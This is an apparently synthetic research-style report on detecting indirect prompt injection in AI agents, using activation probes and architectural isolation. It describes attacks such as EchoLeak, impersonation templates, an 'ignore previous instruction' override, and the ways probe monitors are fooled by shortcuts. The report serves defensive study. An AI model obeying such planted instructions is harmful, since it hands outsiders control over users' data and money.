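# Detecting prompt injection from activations compared with architectural isolation of untrusted data

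## What is prompt injection in a tool-using agent, and what would count as a guarantee against it?

Prompt injection is an attack on software that contains a large language model. An attacker gets text in front of the model, and the model acts on it as if it came from someone entitled to give instructions. AI agents mainly face *indirect prompt injection* ("injection" from here on), in which the attacker plants an instruction in content that the agent will read while working for somebody else, such as a web page, an email or a shared file. One defence checks the model's internal computations for signs of a planted instruction. Another designs the software around the model so that untrusted text cannot determine what the agent does, even when the model mistakes that text for a legitimate instruction.

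### The agent loop and its single stream of text

An agent is a language model that works in a loop, calling tools and reading their results. OpenAI's *Unrolling the Codex agent loop* describes this loop for the company's coding agent. The model receives a prompt and either answers the user or requests a tool call, such as a command that lists the files in a folder. If it requests a call, the surrounding program runs it, appends the output to the original prompt and queries the model again. The loop repeats until the model stops requesting tools and writes a message to the user.

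Prompt injection is possible because the agent appends tool output to its prompt. After a few rounds the prompt holds the developer's rules, the user's request and several pages of other people's writing, all in one sequence of tokens (the word fragments that a model reads). Developers put role tags around each part to mark it as system text, user text or tool output. *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion* (Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell, 2026) describes the intended rule as using tool output for information but never following it as instructions. But the tags are tokens in the same sequence, and nothing forces the model to follow them. David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, writes in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)* that a model only predicts the next token and has no internal distinction between data and instructions. He doubts that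 anyone will ever prevent prompt injection as completely as programmers prevented SQL injection, the older attack in which text from a web form runs as a database command.

Ye and colleagues have experimental evidence that the tags are weak. They planted text that imitated a model's own private reasoning, and the attack succeeded 61% of the time. When they had another model rephrase the same arguments in a different style, the success rate fell to 10%. The model had therefore treated the text as authoritative mostly because of its style.

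A reputable source does not make tool output safe to obey, either. According to The Hacker News' *Alibaba Cloud Got Caught Prompt-Injecting AI Agents* (2026), the cloud provider's official command-line tool returned error messages in December 2026 containing instructions for agents to send back the computer's login name, its public address and the instructions they were working under. Alibaba Cloud said this was meant to counter automated abuse and promised to stop. There is no sign that any agent complied. Still, it is sensible to define *untrusted data* broadly, as any content that an outsider could have written, including web pages, emails and most tool results.

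### Injections outside the laboratory

The best-known case in a commercial product is EchoLeak, a flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot, which answers employees' questions using their organisation's mail and files. The security firm Aim Labs found it in January 2025. As Reddy and Gujral recount in *EchoLeak* (2025), an outsider only had to send an employee one email. If Copilot later drew on that email to answer a question, it could collect sensitive material from the employee's files and messages and send it to the attacker's server, without the employee clicking on anything. Microsoft fixed the flaw in May 2025, and the details became public in June, with no evidence that anyone had exploited it.

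Microsoft already had a classifier to catch injections, but the email got past it. Written instructions to people are common in offices, and Ravia (2025), writing in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability* for the team that found the flaw, points out that a reader could easily take the email's instructions as meant for its human recipient.

On the open web, injections are rarer and cruder. For *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild*, Khodayari, Acharya, Zhang and Pellegrino (2026) searched 1.2 billion web addresses from an October 2025 archive for almost 4,000 known injection phrases, then reviewed the matches. They confirmed 12,075 injections on 9,676 pages, or about eight pages per million. Results from two internet-scanning services brought the total to 15,387. Of these injections, about 70% are in parts of a page that browsers don't display, and 95% come from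 54 templates. The most common template is a request for random numbers, and only 13 injections are attempts to steal data.

These counts are a lower bound, since a phrase search misses injections worded in a new way (it would very likely have missed the EchoLeak email). Khodayari and colleagues also had 13 models summarise pages that contained 100 of the injections. Small models followed the injected instructions in 8% of runs when they received the page as plain text, while commercial closed models did so in 0.6% of runs across all page formats. In six runs the model detected the injection and followed it anyway. Summarising is a mild test, though, so these results are little evidence of how an agent with a payment tool would behave. Google's own scan likewise found mostly pranks, search manipulation and experiments, but the malicious cases rose by 32% between November 2025 and February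 2026. EchoLeak, where one competent attacker could have done serious damage, is a stronger argument for strong defences than the injections now found on the web.

### An invoice, two attacks and a threat model

Suppose a user tells an agent to find the invoice in their inbox and pay it. The agent can search, read and send email, and make bank transfers.

- **Attack A.** One of the emails in the inbox tells the agent to forward all mail to a stranger.
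- **Attack B.** The invoice carries a changed account number. It contains no instruction at all.

Attack A is an injection by any definition. *Prompt-Injection Probes Learn the Conversation, Not Just the Injection* (Kale and Vishwanath, 2026) uses the word for any passage in a tool's results that contains a request the user never made. Attack B falls outside this definition because it contains no request. The agent pays the invoice as the user wanted, but the money goes to the wrong place.

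*Beyond Instruction Override* (Zhang, Bertran and colleagues, 2026) defines an attack by authority instead of wording: planted content is an attack when it tries to influence a decision that its source has no authority to determine. In the paper's example, a buyer's evidence in a dispute gives the refund as $1,074.99, but the user has told the agent to go by the order record, which authorises $899.99. Attack B meets this definition if the user has told the agent to take account numbers from a supplier list. If the user has named no such list, the invoice may well be the proper authority on where to pay it, and the false number is then ordinary misinformation, which takes independent evidence to detect. This report uses "injection" in the narrower sense of a planted instruction, but keeps attack B in the example because a thief can steal the money without an injection.

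Narisetty, Kore and colleagues (2026) remark in *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* that disagreements about whether a defence works are often disagreements about the attacker. In their threat model, which is a common one, the attacker controls the content of at least one untrusted channel, here the inbox. The attacker also knows how the system works, including its defences, and can revise the text and try again, but cannot alter the model's weights, the user's request or the code that enforces the rules.

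Researchers differ more over what the attacker knows about the task. Zhang and colleagues assume an attacker who can guess what sort of jobs the agent does but never sees the request, which fits someone who mails out false invoices. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) reports a large public contest in which attackers saw the whole conversation up to the point of injection and knew the exact tool call they had to provoke.

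It also matters which harm a defence is meant to prevent. Harm to *integrity* means the agent does something its user did not want, or does the right thing with the wrong values. Harm to *confidentiality* means information reaches someone who should not have it. Attack B harms only integrity, because it moves money without leaking any secret. Attack A harms confidentiality, but through an action nobody requested, so a defence that controls actions can stop it. In EchoLeak, however, Copilot had no means of sending email, and the data escaped through the answer it displayed. A defence that checked only actions such as sending mail would have missed the leak.

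### Two defences

A language model passes each token through a stack of layers, and each layer produces a long list of numbers called *activations*, or hidden states. A *linear probe* multiplies each number by a learned weight and turns the sum into a score. Training adjusts the weights until examples containing an injection get high scores and the rest get low ones. A monitor then flags any tool output whose score passes a threshold. Because the model computes its activations anyway, the probe adds very little computation. Kale and Vishwanath note that Anthropic runs injection probes on tool outputs across many of its products. Such a probe typically serves as a first filter, which doesn't block anything itself but sends what it flags to a slower check, such as a second language model. In the invoice example, the probe ought to flag attack A, but attack B contains no instruction for it to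 detect.

Researchers usually grade a detector by its *AUROC*, the chance that it scores a random attack above a random harmless case. Random guessing scores 0.5 and perfect ranking scores 1.0. AUROC doesn't determine how many false alarms a team will see, which depends on the threshold and on the *false-positive rate*, the share of harmless cases that the detector flags. If injections were as rare in tool outputs as Khodayari and colleagues found them on web pages, a detector that caught every attack and flagged 1% of harmless outputs would produce about 10,000 false alarms and eight correct alarms per million outputs.

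*Architectural isolation* assumes that some injections will fool the model. In one design, a planner model sees only the user's request and writes out the steps: find the invoice, read off the amount and the account, and pay. A quarantined model, which has no tools, reads the email and returns those two values. Ordinary code carries out the plan and labels each value with its *provenance*, the sources it came from. Before paying, the code checks the labels against a rule. Attack A fails because the plan has no step for forwarding mail and the quarantined model cannot add one. In attack B, the changed account number is a value the plan calls for. Its label shows that it came from an outsider's email, so the rule can either halt the payment and ask the user or let it through, but the code cannot check whether the number is genuine. David C recommends prioritizing deterministic safeguards like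 these, which limit what the system can do, over attempts to keep malicious content away from the model.

### AgentDojo, the shared test bed

Researchers test both defences on *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024), a benchmark that simulates four applications, each with its own tools, user tasks and attacker tasks. It pairs every user task with every attacker task in the same application.

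| Application | User tasks | Attacker tasks | Pairs | Example of an attacker task |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace (email, calendar, files) | 40 | 6 | 240 | Send a security code to the attacker |
| Slack (team messages, web pages) | 21 | 5 | 105 | Send a colleague a phishing link |
| Travel | 20 | 7 | 140 | Book the most expensive hotel in Paris |
| Banking | 16 | 9 | 144 | Send as much money as possible to the attacker |
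| Total | 97 | 27 | 629 | |

The benchmark places the attacker's text where an outsider could plausibly have written, such as in the body of an email. After each run, a short piece of code checks the simulated application's state, for instance whether a transfer went out. Debenedetti and colleagues chose code over a language-model judge because an injection that hijacks the agent might hijack the judge as well. They report three figures: *benign utility*, the share of user tasks the agent completes without an attack; *utility under attack*, the share of pairs in which it completes the user's task without harmful side effects; and *attack success rate*, the share of pairs in which it carries out the attacker's goal. In 2024, every model completed less than 66% of the tasks even without an attack. Attacks on the best agents succeeded in under 25% of pairs, and adding a separate detector reduced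 that to 8%. The benchmark has since grown to more than 900 pairs, according to *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026).

One of AgentDojo's banking tasks asks the agent to pay a bill that it must read from a file, which is nearly the invoice example. But AgentDojo's attacker goals are all written as instructions to the agent, so it tests for attack A and provides little evidence about attack B.

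### Three strengths of claim

A *success rate on a fixed attack set*, such as the 8% above, is the easiest claim to make and the weakest. Even zero successes in 629 independent trials would be compatible with a true rate of nearly 0.5%, and that figure applies only to attacks like the ones in the set, while real attackers can write others. Debenedetti and colleagues themselves warn that it is extremely easy to build a defence that thwarts any specific attack.

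A *success rate under adaptive attack with a stated budget* is more informative. The attacker designs or refines the attack against the defence in place, and the researchers report how many attempts were allowed. In the contest that Dziemian and colleagues ran, 464 people made about 272,000 attempts on 13 models, and the success rate per attempt ranged from 0.5% for Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5% for Gemini 2.5 Pro. The number of attempts matters a great deal. Anthropic's figures for Claude Opus 4.5 in coding tasks, quoted by Narisetty and colleagues, put an automated attacker's success rate at 4.7% after one attempt, 33.6% after ten and 63.0% after a hundred. If each attempt had had an independent 4.7% chance, the rate would have been about 38% after ten attempts and 99% after a hundred, so some targets were probably much harder to attack than others. The two single-attempt rates for this model,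 0.5% and 4.7%, differ ninefold, but the scenarios were different and the contest also required attackers to hide the attack from the user. Such rates therefore depend on the attacker and the setting as well as the defence.

A *guarantee* is a property that holds for every untrusted input, given a list of assumptions. Write *u* for the user's request, *x* for all the untrusted data that the agent reads, and *A*(*u*, *x*) for the consequential actions that result. The strictest guarantee of integrity would be

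*A*(*u*, *x*) = *A*(*u*, *x*′) for every *x* and *x*′.

This formula includes no budget because it already covers texts that nobody has thought of yet. It would defeat both attacks, but it would also make the invoice impossible to pay, since the amount has to come from the inbox. Useful guarantees are therefore weaker. One might be that untrusted data cannot change which tools the agent calls, which stops attack A but not attack B. Another might be that every recipient of money or mail comes from a trusted source. That stops both attacks if somebody maintains a trusted list of accounts, but the agent could still pay an inflated amount.

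Such a guarantee holds only if the enforcing code works as designed, the labels are right, and the user's own message deserves the trust the system places in it. The last condition fails if the user has pasted in a stranger's text. From here on, "guarantee" has only this meaning. A low attack success rate, however low, does not count as one, though it may still be well worth having. Narisetty and colleagues argue that detectors and special training cannot guarantee anything against an adaptive attacker, because the model does not reliably separate instructions from data, but they would still use them as one layer among several.

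## How can a model's activations reveal an injected instruction?

Injection probes rely on the fact that a model's activations after it reads a planted instruction differ fairly consistently from its activations after harmless text. Nobody designed models to produce this difference. Researchers found it by training small classifiers on activations and testing them on attacks that were not in the training data. The model may still obey the instruction, and much of the recent work is about why.

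### From activations to a score

The activations at each token form a vector of a few thousand numbers. Each layer adds its result to that vector, and researchers call the running total the *residual stream*. Layers can bring in information from earlier tokens, so the vector at the end of a prompt can reflect everything before it. Most probes therefore read the vector at the last token or one close to it.

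Call this vector *h*. A linear probe computes

*z* = *w* · *h* + *b*,  *p* = 1 / (1 + e^(−*z*)).

Here *w* · *h* is the weighted sum of the activations, and *b* is a constant that shifts it. The second formula, the *sigmoid*, converts *z* into a probability between 0 and 1. A *z* of 0 becomes 0.5, and a *z* of 3 becomes about 0.95. *w* is a direction in the space of activations, and the score measures how far *h* lies along it. Training uses examples labeled *y* = 1 for an injection and *y* = 0 otherwise. It leaves the language model unchanged and adjusts only *w* and *b* to reduce the average of −[*y* log *p* + (1 − *y*) log(1 − *p*)]. This penalty grows steeply when the probe assigns a high probability to the wrong label.

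In an agent, the natural place to read *h* is just after a tool result. In *Your Agentic LLMs Secretly Encode Indirect Prompt-Injection Exposure in Hidden States*, Dong, Liu and colleagues (2026) read it from the tokens that open the model's next turn, before the model has written anything. A monitor can therefore compute its score before the next tool call. For Qwen3-8B, the best probes near this boundary reach an AUROC of 0.97 to 0.98 on unfamiliar attacks, compared with 0.935 for probes that read the activations after the model has finished reasoning and 0.794 for probes that read them after it has written its tool call.

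Labeling examples is easy because researchers plant the attacks themselves and know where they are. They still have to decide what counts as a positive example. Dong and colleagues label a turn positive if the most recent tool result contains an attack, regardless of what the model does next.

### Detectors for single documents

The first detectors of this type handled one user request and one retrieved text. *Get my drift?* (Abdelnabi, Fay and colleagues, 2024) introduced TaskTracker, which runs the model on the user's request alone, then on the request plus the text. Both times, it adds a sentence asking the model to list the requests it is about to carry out. It subtracts the first run's last-token activations from the second's and gives the difference to a linear classifier. The subtraction removes much of what the user's request contributes, so the difference should mostly reflect the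 text.

Abdelnabi and colleagues trained probes on encyclopedia paragraphs with ordinary tasks inserted, such as trivia questions, and tested them on malicious requests, jailbreaks and coding tasks. The AUROC was at least 0.99 on six models. In one control, they wrote injected questions into clean paragraphs as normal prose, along the lines of "you may be wondering what the capital of France is". In a small Phi-3 model, a probe on an early layer could barely distinguish these from the injected versions (AUROC 0.577), but from the middle layers onward the score was about 0.99. The deeper activations therefore reflect whether a question is put to the model, not just whether the text contains one. On a harder private collection with long documents, tool use and subtle phrasing, the score fell to 0.934, and retraining on similar data raised it to 0.989.

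*Attention Tracker* (Hung, Ko and colleagues, 2024) uses a different internal signal, the model's attention weights. Each layer contains several *attention heads*, and each head divides a fixed total of weight among the preceding tokens, which determines how much information it draws from each. Hung and colleagues noticed that in certain heads, an injection shifts weight from the user's instruction to the planted one. To find those heads, they took 30 random sentences, added a crude "ignore previous instruction" attack to a copy of each, and measured how much weight each head placed on the real instruction when processing the last token. They kept a head only if its average on clean text minus four standard deviations was higher than its average under attack plus four standard deviations. The detector averages the weight on the user's instruction across the selected heads and flags an injection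 when this average, the *focus score*, falls below a threshold.

This method worked well on short, single-turn prompts but badly in agents. In *Attention-based Classification for Indirect Prompt Injection*, Kawasaki and Lee (2026) measured an average AUROC of 0.97 on a single-turn collection but 0.57 on AgentDojo, barely better than guessing. On long, structured tool outputs, the focus scores of clean and attacked inputs largely overlap. In one small model, about 42% of heads put *more* weight on the user's instruction during an attack, contrary to the method's assumption. They then gave every head its own learned weight, positive or negative, and reached 0.94 after training on AgentDojo examples, but only 0.62 after training on synthetic sentences. They had just 51 AgentDojo samples, so the exact figures are rough, but the gap between 0.57 and 0.97 is large enough to take seriously.

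Two later detectors drop the comparison with the user's request and look only for an instruction in the data. Zou, Liu and colleagues (2025) trained the simpler one, *PIShield*, on 10,000 clean passages and 10,000 with an inserted instruction. They fitted a linear probe to the last token's activations at every layer and kept the layer that did best on a validation set. On average, the probe flagged 0.5% of clean texts and missed 1.4% of attacks. *Defending against Indirect Prompt Injection by Instruction Detection* (Wen, Wang and colleagues, 2025) presents InstructDetector, which uses gradients as well as activations. To compute the gradients, it pairs the text with the reply "Sure", a typical response to an order, and calculates how the attention layers' weights would have to change to make that reply more likely. A small neural network then classifies the gradients and activations together.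 Trained on only 200 examples, it classified 99.6% of texts correctly on familiar kinds of data and 96.9% on unfamiliar ones. Without the gradients, the second figure was still 96.2%, so the activations provide nearly all of the useful information, and the gradients require a computationally intensive backward pass through the model.

Zou and colleagues state that both methods assume injected content is itself an instruction. Their clean training texts came from encyclopedia passages and the data half of an instruction collection, which contain few instructions. Office mail contains more, so a false-positive rate of 0.5% on question-answering benchmarks is weak evidence of how often such a probe would flag it.

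### Probing agents at work

Dong and colleagues ran the largest test in agents. They ran eight open models on AgentDojo, from Qwen3.5-2B (two billion parameters) to Kimi-K3 (2.8 trillion). Each setting combined one of the benchmark's four applications, one of four system prompts and one of six attack templates. The templates ranged from a bare "TODO" followed by the attacker's goal to a message written as if it came from the user, addressing the model by name. One template does not fit the workspace application, which leaves 92 settings. With three runs per attack, they planned 61,608 runs for each model except Kimi-K3, which was tested on only part of the grid.

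In AgentDojo, the agent sees the attack text only if it opens the item that contains it. In many runs it never does, and in the rest, many turns come before it does. The turns without attack text serve as harmless examples from the same environment. Depending on the model, 13% to 23% of turns counted as exposed to the attack. A real agent would normally encounter attacks far less often, so a larger share of alarms would be false in practice.

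The probes trained on eight settings, which covered two applications, two templates and two system prompts. The hardest test, the *strict* split, used 16 settings in which the application, the template and the system prompt were all new. A probe that had learned to detect attacks in Slack messages therefore had to recognise differently worded attacks in bank records. AUROC on this split ranged from 0.934 to 0.979 across the eight models, while random directions averaged 0.46 to 0.59. Model size made no clear difference, and the smallest model had the highest score. The best layer ranged from the second of 32 in Qwen3.5-9B to the second-last of 93 in Kimi-K3. Dong and colleagues chose which layer to report by its score on the strict split itself, so these figures are somewhat inflated. Anyone deploying a probe would have to choose the layer using separate data.

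The signal also transferred further than the split required:

- **Other benchmarks.** A Qwen3-8B probe trained on AgentDojo scored 0.965 on about 15,000 turns from InjecAgent and AgentDyn, two other collections of attacks on agents.
- **Chinese.** On a Chinese copy of AgentDojo, a probe trained in English scored 0.940. One trained in Chinese scored 0.953 on the English original.
- **Other models' transcripts.** Qwen3-8B reread conversations that other models had produced, and its probe did about as well on them as each model's own probe.

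Kawasaki and Lee got a much worse result from a similar classifier, an average of 0.58 when they trained on one data set and tested on another. But they read only the final layer, and some of their training sets were tiny. Dong and colleagues saw a smaller version of the same weakness. With few examples, their probes fitted the training data quickly but did noticeably worse on the strict split. The gap narrowed as the training set grew, and at 256 examples the strict score was 0.909. Transfer seems to depend heavily on the amount and variety of training data, and a high AUROC alone does not show that a probe has learned to recognise injections themselves.

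### Exposure and compliance

These probes mainly measure *exposure*, which is whether the model has just read an injection, rather than *compliance*, which is whether it does what the injection asks. In Abdelnabi and colleagues' tests of TaskTracker, activations shifted by about the same amount whether or not the model carried out the injected task. When Dong and colleagues retrained their Qwen3-8B probe to predict whether the attack would eventually succeed, its AUROC was between 0.825 and 0.891 on the held-out sets, compared with 0.976 for exposure on the strict split. The lower scores are unsurprising because compliance also depends on what the model does later.

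GLM-5.2, a model with 753 billion parameters, encountered an injection in 39,800 runs and carried out the attacker's goal in about 160 of them (0.4%). A perfect exposure probe would have raised an alarm in all 39,800. Alarms for the failed attacks are still useful because they show which emails and pages an attacker has reached, but stopping the agent every time would interrupt thousands of tasks that would have gone well. *DriftNet* (Pinjari and Saint-Germain, 2026) describes a system called BASIS that tries to solve this problem by using probes to separate inputs the model would resist from inputs that would hijack it, and refusing only the second group.

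In weaker models the opposite problem is more serious, since the probe detects the injection and the model obeys it anyway. Dong and colleagues call this the *knowledge–action gap*. They examined 634 turns at which Qwen3-8B had just read an injection and the probe had correctly flagged it, and had another model classify the written reasoning and the action that followed:

- In 31% of turns, the reasoning did not mention any risk.
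- In 47%, it recognised the risk, but the turn still contained no effective defence, and in some cases the action advanced the attacker's goal.
- In 22%, it recognised the risk and the action was safe.

In the most common failure, the danger was identified in the model's reasoning but this had no effect on its action. These turns came from the hardest settings, so the shares do not describe Qwen3-8B in general.

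Dong and colleagues also probed the base versions of two models, which had not yet had the training that turns a text predictor into an assistant. The AUROC was already 0.964 for Qwen3-8B and 0.945 for Qwen3.5-9B, so the signal does not come from safety training. They hypothesize that later training fails to connect the signal reliably to the model's choice of action. Calling the signal "knowledge" is perhaps too strong, because a probe can find information in activations that the rest of the model never uses.

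### Using the probe to trigger a reminder

If the information is present in the activations but does not affect the model's action, one remedy is to state it in the model's reasoning. Dong and colleagues insert a short passage at the start of the reasoning whenever the probe's score exceeds 0.5. The passage is written as if by the model and states that a tool result may contain a side task, that the model must not carry it out, and that it will return to the user's request and take only facts from the tool output. They keep using the passage for the next three turns in case the attack takes effect later.

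The test covered the eight hardest settings from banking and travel, with 3,408 attack attempts per model. Each cell below gives the attack success rate, then utility on clean tasks, both as percentages.

| Model | No defence | Reminder after every tool result | Inserted reasoning at every turn | Inserted reasoning when the probe fires |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3-8B | 47.2 / 65.6 | 18.2 / 68.0 | 3.6 / 54.3 | 2.9 / 69.1 |
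| Qwen3.5-2B | 7.7 / 50.7 | 8.5 / 47.9 | 2.3 / 29.2 | 3.2 / 50.0 |
| Qwen3.5-9B | 43.2 / 93.8 | 7.6 / 90.7 | 2.7 / 82.6 | 3.0 / 88.2 |
| Qwen3.5-27B | 34.6 / 92.4 | 0.1 / 89.0 | 0.0 / 82.4 | 0.0 / 89.7 |
| GPT-oss-20B | 44.0 / 70.6 | 15.0 / 66.3 | 7.0 / 56.0 | 7.0 / 66.8 |
| Gemma-4-31B | 6.9 / 91.4 | 0.0 / 93.5 | 0.0 / 91.1 | 0.0 / 91.8 |

Attack success fell from 34.6% to 0.0% on Qwen3.5-27B and from 47.2% to 2.9% on Qwen3-8B. The last two columns show nearly equal attack success, so the inserted text is what stops the attacks. The probe helps preserve utility on clean tasks. Qwen3-8B's utility fell to 54.3% when the text was inserted at every turn, but stayed at 69.1% when it was inserted only on an alarm. On Qwen3.5-27B, a plain reminder after every tool result, with no probe, did almost as well. The case for the probe is strongest for models like Qwen3-8B and GPT-oss-20B, where plain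 reminders still let through 15% to 18% of attacks.

This does not guarantee that an attack will fail. Across 4,260 Qwen3-8B runs at various thresholds, Dong and colleagues found 108 in which the probe fired and the model received the inserted text, but the attack still succeeded. In one, the user asked for a French restaurant in Paris that opens on Sundays. The model restated the safety rule in its reasoning, worked through the options and correctly chose Breizh Café. It then followed the injected instruction to email its answer to a stranger. Nothing outside the model checked the action, and the tests used only fixed attacks.

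### What the signal may represent

A high AUROC shows that the activations contain something that predicts exposure, but not what it is. To investigate this, Dong and colleagues inserted multiple-choice questions at the start of a model's reasoning and compared its answers with the probe's score, testing 128 candidate statements. "Prompt-injection risk is present" did not rank first for any model, and its rank ranged from 3rd to 87th. For two of the Qwen models, the best match was a statement that a tool output contains a directive about how to respond. For the three models that attacks hijacked least often, the best match was a statement about injected instructions influencing the model's own planned response. This may be a clue to why those models resist attacks, but it is a correlation among eight models.

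The statement about directives in tool output is close to what Ye and colleagues call *role confusion*. The earlier result about imitated reasoning showed that style can override role tags, and Ye and colleagues use *role probes* to look for the same effect inside the model. They wrapped each passage of ordinary web text in each of five role tags and trained a linear classifier to tell from the activations which tag was in use. Because the passages were the same for every tag, the classifier could learn only the effect of the tag. They then applied it to real user messages inside tool-output tags. Across four models, the probe assigned these messages a 76% to 88% probability of being user text and at most a 20% probability of being tool output.

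This measure also predicts compliance. Ye and colleagues ran 1,000 attempts to make an agent upload a secret file, using the same command each time but changing the text around it. The success rate rose from 2% where the command registered least strongly as user text to 70% where it registered most strongly. Simply stating that the following text came from the user often raised the score. Ye and colleagues suggest that a monitor might flag passages whose apparent role conflicts with their tag, but leave this as an open question. Such a monitor would face the same problem with inboxes, since a colleague's request can sound like a user's without being an attack.

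Probes can also distinguish two uses of the same words, however, so style does not explain everything. *Readable Before Actionable* (Yu, Xing and colleagues, 2026) used prompts that contained commands such as "Calculate 24 plus 76" and asked the model either to execute the command or to summarise a note that consisted of it. Linear probes told the two uses apart with an AUROC of 0.924 on Qwen-2.5-7B and 0.918 on Llama-3.1-8B, even when the test data reversed the training data's link between the command's role and quotation marks. A classifier that used only length, position, punctuation and similar features scored 0.508. These results are compatible with those of Ye and colleagues, because the user's own words explain what the command is for in these prompts, whereas Ye and colleagues gave the model only a tag.

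Yu and colleagues then tested whether changing the signal changes behaviour. They ran one prompt that called for a weather tool and another that called for a calculator. They copied the first prompt's activations into the second, but only the component along the direction that separates instructions from data. Up to layer 16, this never changed the model's choice of tool. At layers 18 to 22, it changed the choice in 82% to 98% of cases, while copying everything except that component changed it in only 4% to 7%. The role of a command can therefore be read in layers where editing it has little effect.

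This does not prove that the model normally uses this direction to decide what to obey, because the two prompts needed different tools and both were genuine requests. The direction also failed to carry over to real attacks. On AgentDojo's Slack tasks, it left the attack success rate near the original 34.6%, while a direction computed from hijacked and resisted Slack runs reduced the rate to 21.2%. Directions computed from one kind of source had little effect on another. A probe that detects injections well is therefore a poor guide to where to edit the model, and it may be easier to respond to its alarm from outside the model, by adding text or blocking a tool call.

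### Who can run a probe

A probe needs the model's activations, so only someone who runs the model can use one directly. That means the company that built it or, if the model is open, anyone who hosts it. A customer who uses a closed model through an API receives only text.

Such a customer can have a second, open model read the same tool results. Wen and colleagues used an eight-billion-parameter Llama model to screen documents for GPT-3.5-Turbo, and the attack success rate fell from 33.6% to 0.12% on a benchmark of fixed attacks. Zou and colleagues recommend the same arrangement when the main model is closed, and Qwen3-8B's success on other models' transcripts supports it. This requires one extra pass through a small model per tool result. However, the second model's activations show how that model processes the text, so they are reasonable evidence that the main model has been exposed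 to an injection but much weaker evidence of whether it will comply.

A defender without access to activations can still analyse the log of tool calls. Pinjari and Saint-Germain trained a small network to do this, and on synthetic runs it found the exact point of entry in 98.7% of successful attacks. Because the network analyses actions the agent has already taken, it is better suited to investigating attacks than to preventing them.

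### The invoice again

In attack A, the probe computes its score after the model reads the email with the forwarding instruction and before the model starts its own turn. The instruction closely resembles the attacks in the training data, so the score should be high. The monitor can then block the next call, ask the user or insert a warning.

An injected instruction may take effect several turns after it arrives. For example, the email might ask the agent to forward the mail only after it has paid the invoice. Two or three tool results later, the instruction is still in the prompt but no longer in the latest result. Dong and colleagues trained a probe to recognise an injection anywhere earlier in the conversation, and its AUROC was lower, between 0.874 and 0.932. A monitor should therefore keep an alarm active for the rest of the task instead of relying on a new score at each turn.

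In attack B, the genuine invoice and the altered one differ only in the digits of the account number. The activations will differ slightly, but nothing in the probe's training links those digits to an attack, so the two scores should be nearly the same. Lowering the threshold would not help, because the probe would then flag genuine invoices as well. TaskTracker has no change of task to detect, and Attention Tracker has no shift in attention to detect, because there is no rival instruction. Even a perfect predictor of compliance would not flag the altered invoice, since the agent is doing exactly what the user asked.

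The email does not contain the fact about the supplier that makes the number false. Pinjari and Saint-Germain similarly argue that the text of a step alone cannot show whether forwarding a document is routine or theft, because that depends on whether the recipient is among the user's known contacts.

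## Do the probes detect the injection or something that accompanies it?

A probe learns any pattern that separates its two sets of training examples, whether or not the pattern has anything to do with injections. Suppose every attacked email in the training set is longer than every clean one. A direction in the activations that tracks length then reduces the training penalty about as well as one that tracks planted requests, so the probe may use either or a mixture. Relying on length would be *shortcut learning*, and the probe would then misclassify long harmless emails and short attacks. Researchers usually guard against shortcuts by testing on examples the probe has never seen, but if attacks are longer in the test set too, the shortcut still produces a high AUROC.

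### A banner full of gibberish

In *When AUC 0.998 Is Not Enough*, Li, Fan and Zhuang (2026) tested probes on Qwen2.5-VL-7B, a model that reads screenshots as well as text. They replayed 80 recorded web-browsing tasks and planted one injection in each. In separate experiments, the injection was a banner drawn on the screenshot, a piece of the page's accessibility text (which describes the page to screen readers), or part of a tool's reply.

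The probe for banners reached an AUROC of 0.998. Li and colleagues then kept this probe and changed only what the banner contained, not its position, font or colour. The probe told gibberish banners from clean screenshots equally well (0.998), but its AUROC for telling real attacks from gibberish was 0.489, about chance. It easily told attacks from a coloured rectangle with no text (0.990), so it had apparently learned to detect writing in a banner. It did somewhat better than chance at telling attacks from harmless interface instructions (0.718), so it may have some sensitivity to meaning, but there were only five such instructions and 20 test tasks.

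The two probes for injected text did much worse, with AUROCs of 0.705 and 0.771. A logistic regression reached 1.000 in both cases using four numbers, none of them taken from the model: the current step, the number of steps in the task, the length of the prompt, and how much longer the prompt was than the clean version of the same step. The last number is enough to separate the two classes, since it is zero for every clean example and positive for every attack, but a working monitor would have no clean copy to compare with. The perfect score therefore shows that the test is flawed, not that the probes relied on length. A better reason to doubt the probes is that they usually scored harmless text of similar length in the same place higher than injected text (AUROC about 0.36).

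Dong and colleagues reply that 80 tasks are few enough to encourage shortcuts, and that the gap between their own probes' training and strict-split scores narrowed with more data. This is a good answer for shortcuts specific to the training settings, such as the wording of one attack template. However, every strict setting comes from AgentDojo, so a pattern found throughout the benchmark would raise both scores.

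Holding out entire data sets from training is a harder test. Fomin (2026), in *When Benchmarks Lie*, trained probes on 18 collections of prompts, which included jailbreaks and harmful requests as well as injections. On Llama-3.1-8B, the AUROC was 0.996 when training and test examples came from the same collections, but 0.912 when the test collection was excluded from training. Across four models, AUROC fell by 8.0 to 16.5 points. One collection consists of ordinary emails from the energy company Enron. The probe flagged 0.8% of them when it had been trained on other Enron emails and 17.4% when it had not.

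Eleven of the collections are entirely malicious or entirely harmless, so a probe can classify their examples correctly just by recognising the collection. A classifier could identify the collection from the activations 89% of the time. Fomin does not attribute the whole gap to shortcuts, because removing 14 features that looked like shortcuts changed the AUROC by only 0.1 points.

### Seven numbers that nearly match the probe

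Kale and Vishwanath used far more data to look for shortcuts in text agents. They applied Dong and colleagues' training recipe to six open models with 8 to 31 billion parameters and collected about 23,000 AgentDojo runs from each model.

In that recipe, the negatives come from the same attacked runs as the positives, at moments before the agent opened the poisoned item or after it had moved on. They therefore differ from the positives in their position in the conversation as well as in the injection.

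Kale and Vishwanath tested how well injections can be detected from position and length alone by fitting a logistic regression to seven numbers. Four describe position: the step number, the number of messages so far, the number of tool outputs so far, and whether the latest message is a tool output. The other three are the lengths of the prompt, the latest tool output and all tool outputs together. This baseline reached an AUROC of 0.96 to 0.98 in applications it had trained on and 0.91 to 0.96 in new ones, while the probes reached 0.97 to 1.00. The position numbers alone gave 0.80 to 0.86. Position and length still help in new applications because AgentDojo's injections arrive at predictable moments and lengthen the tool output in all four applications.

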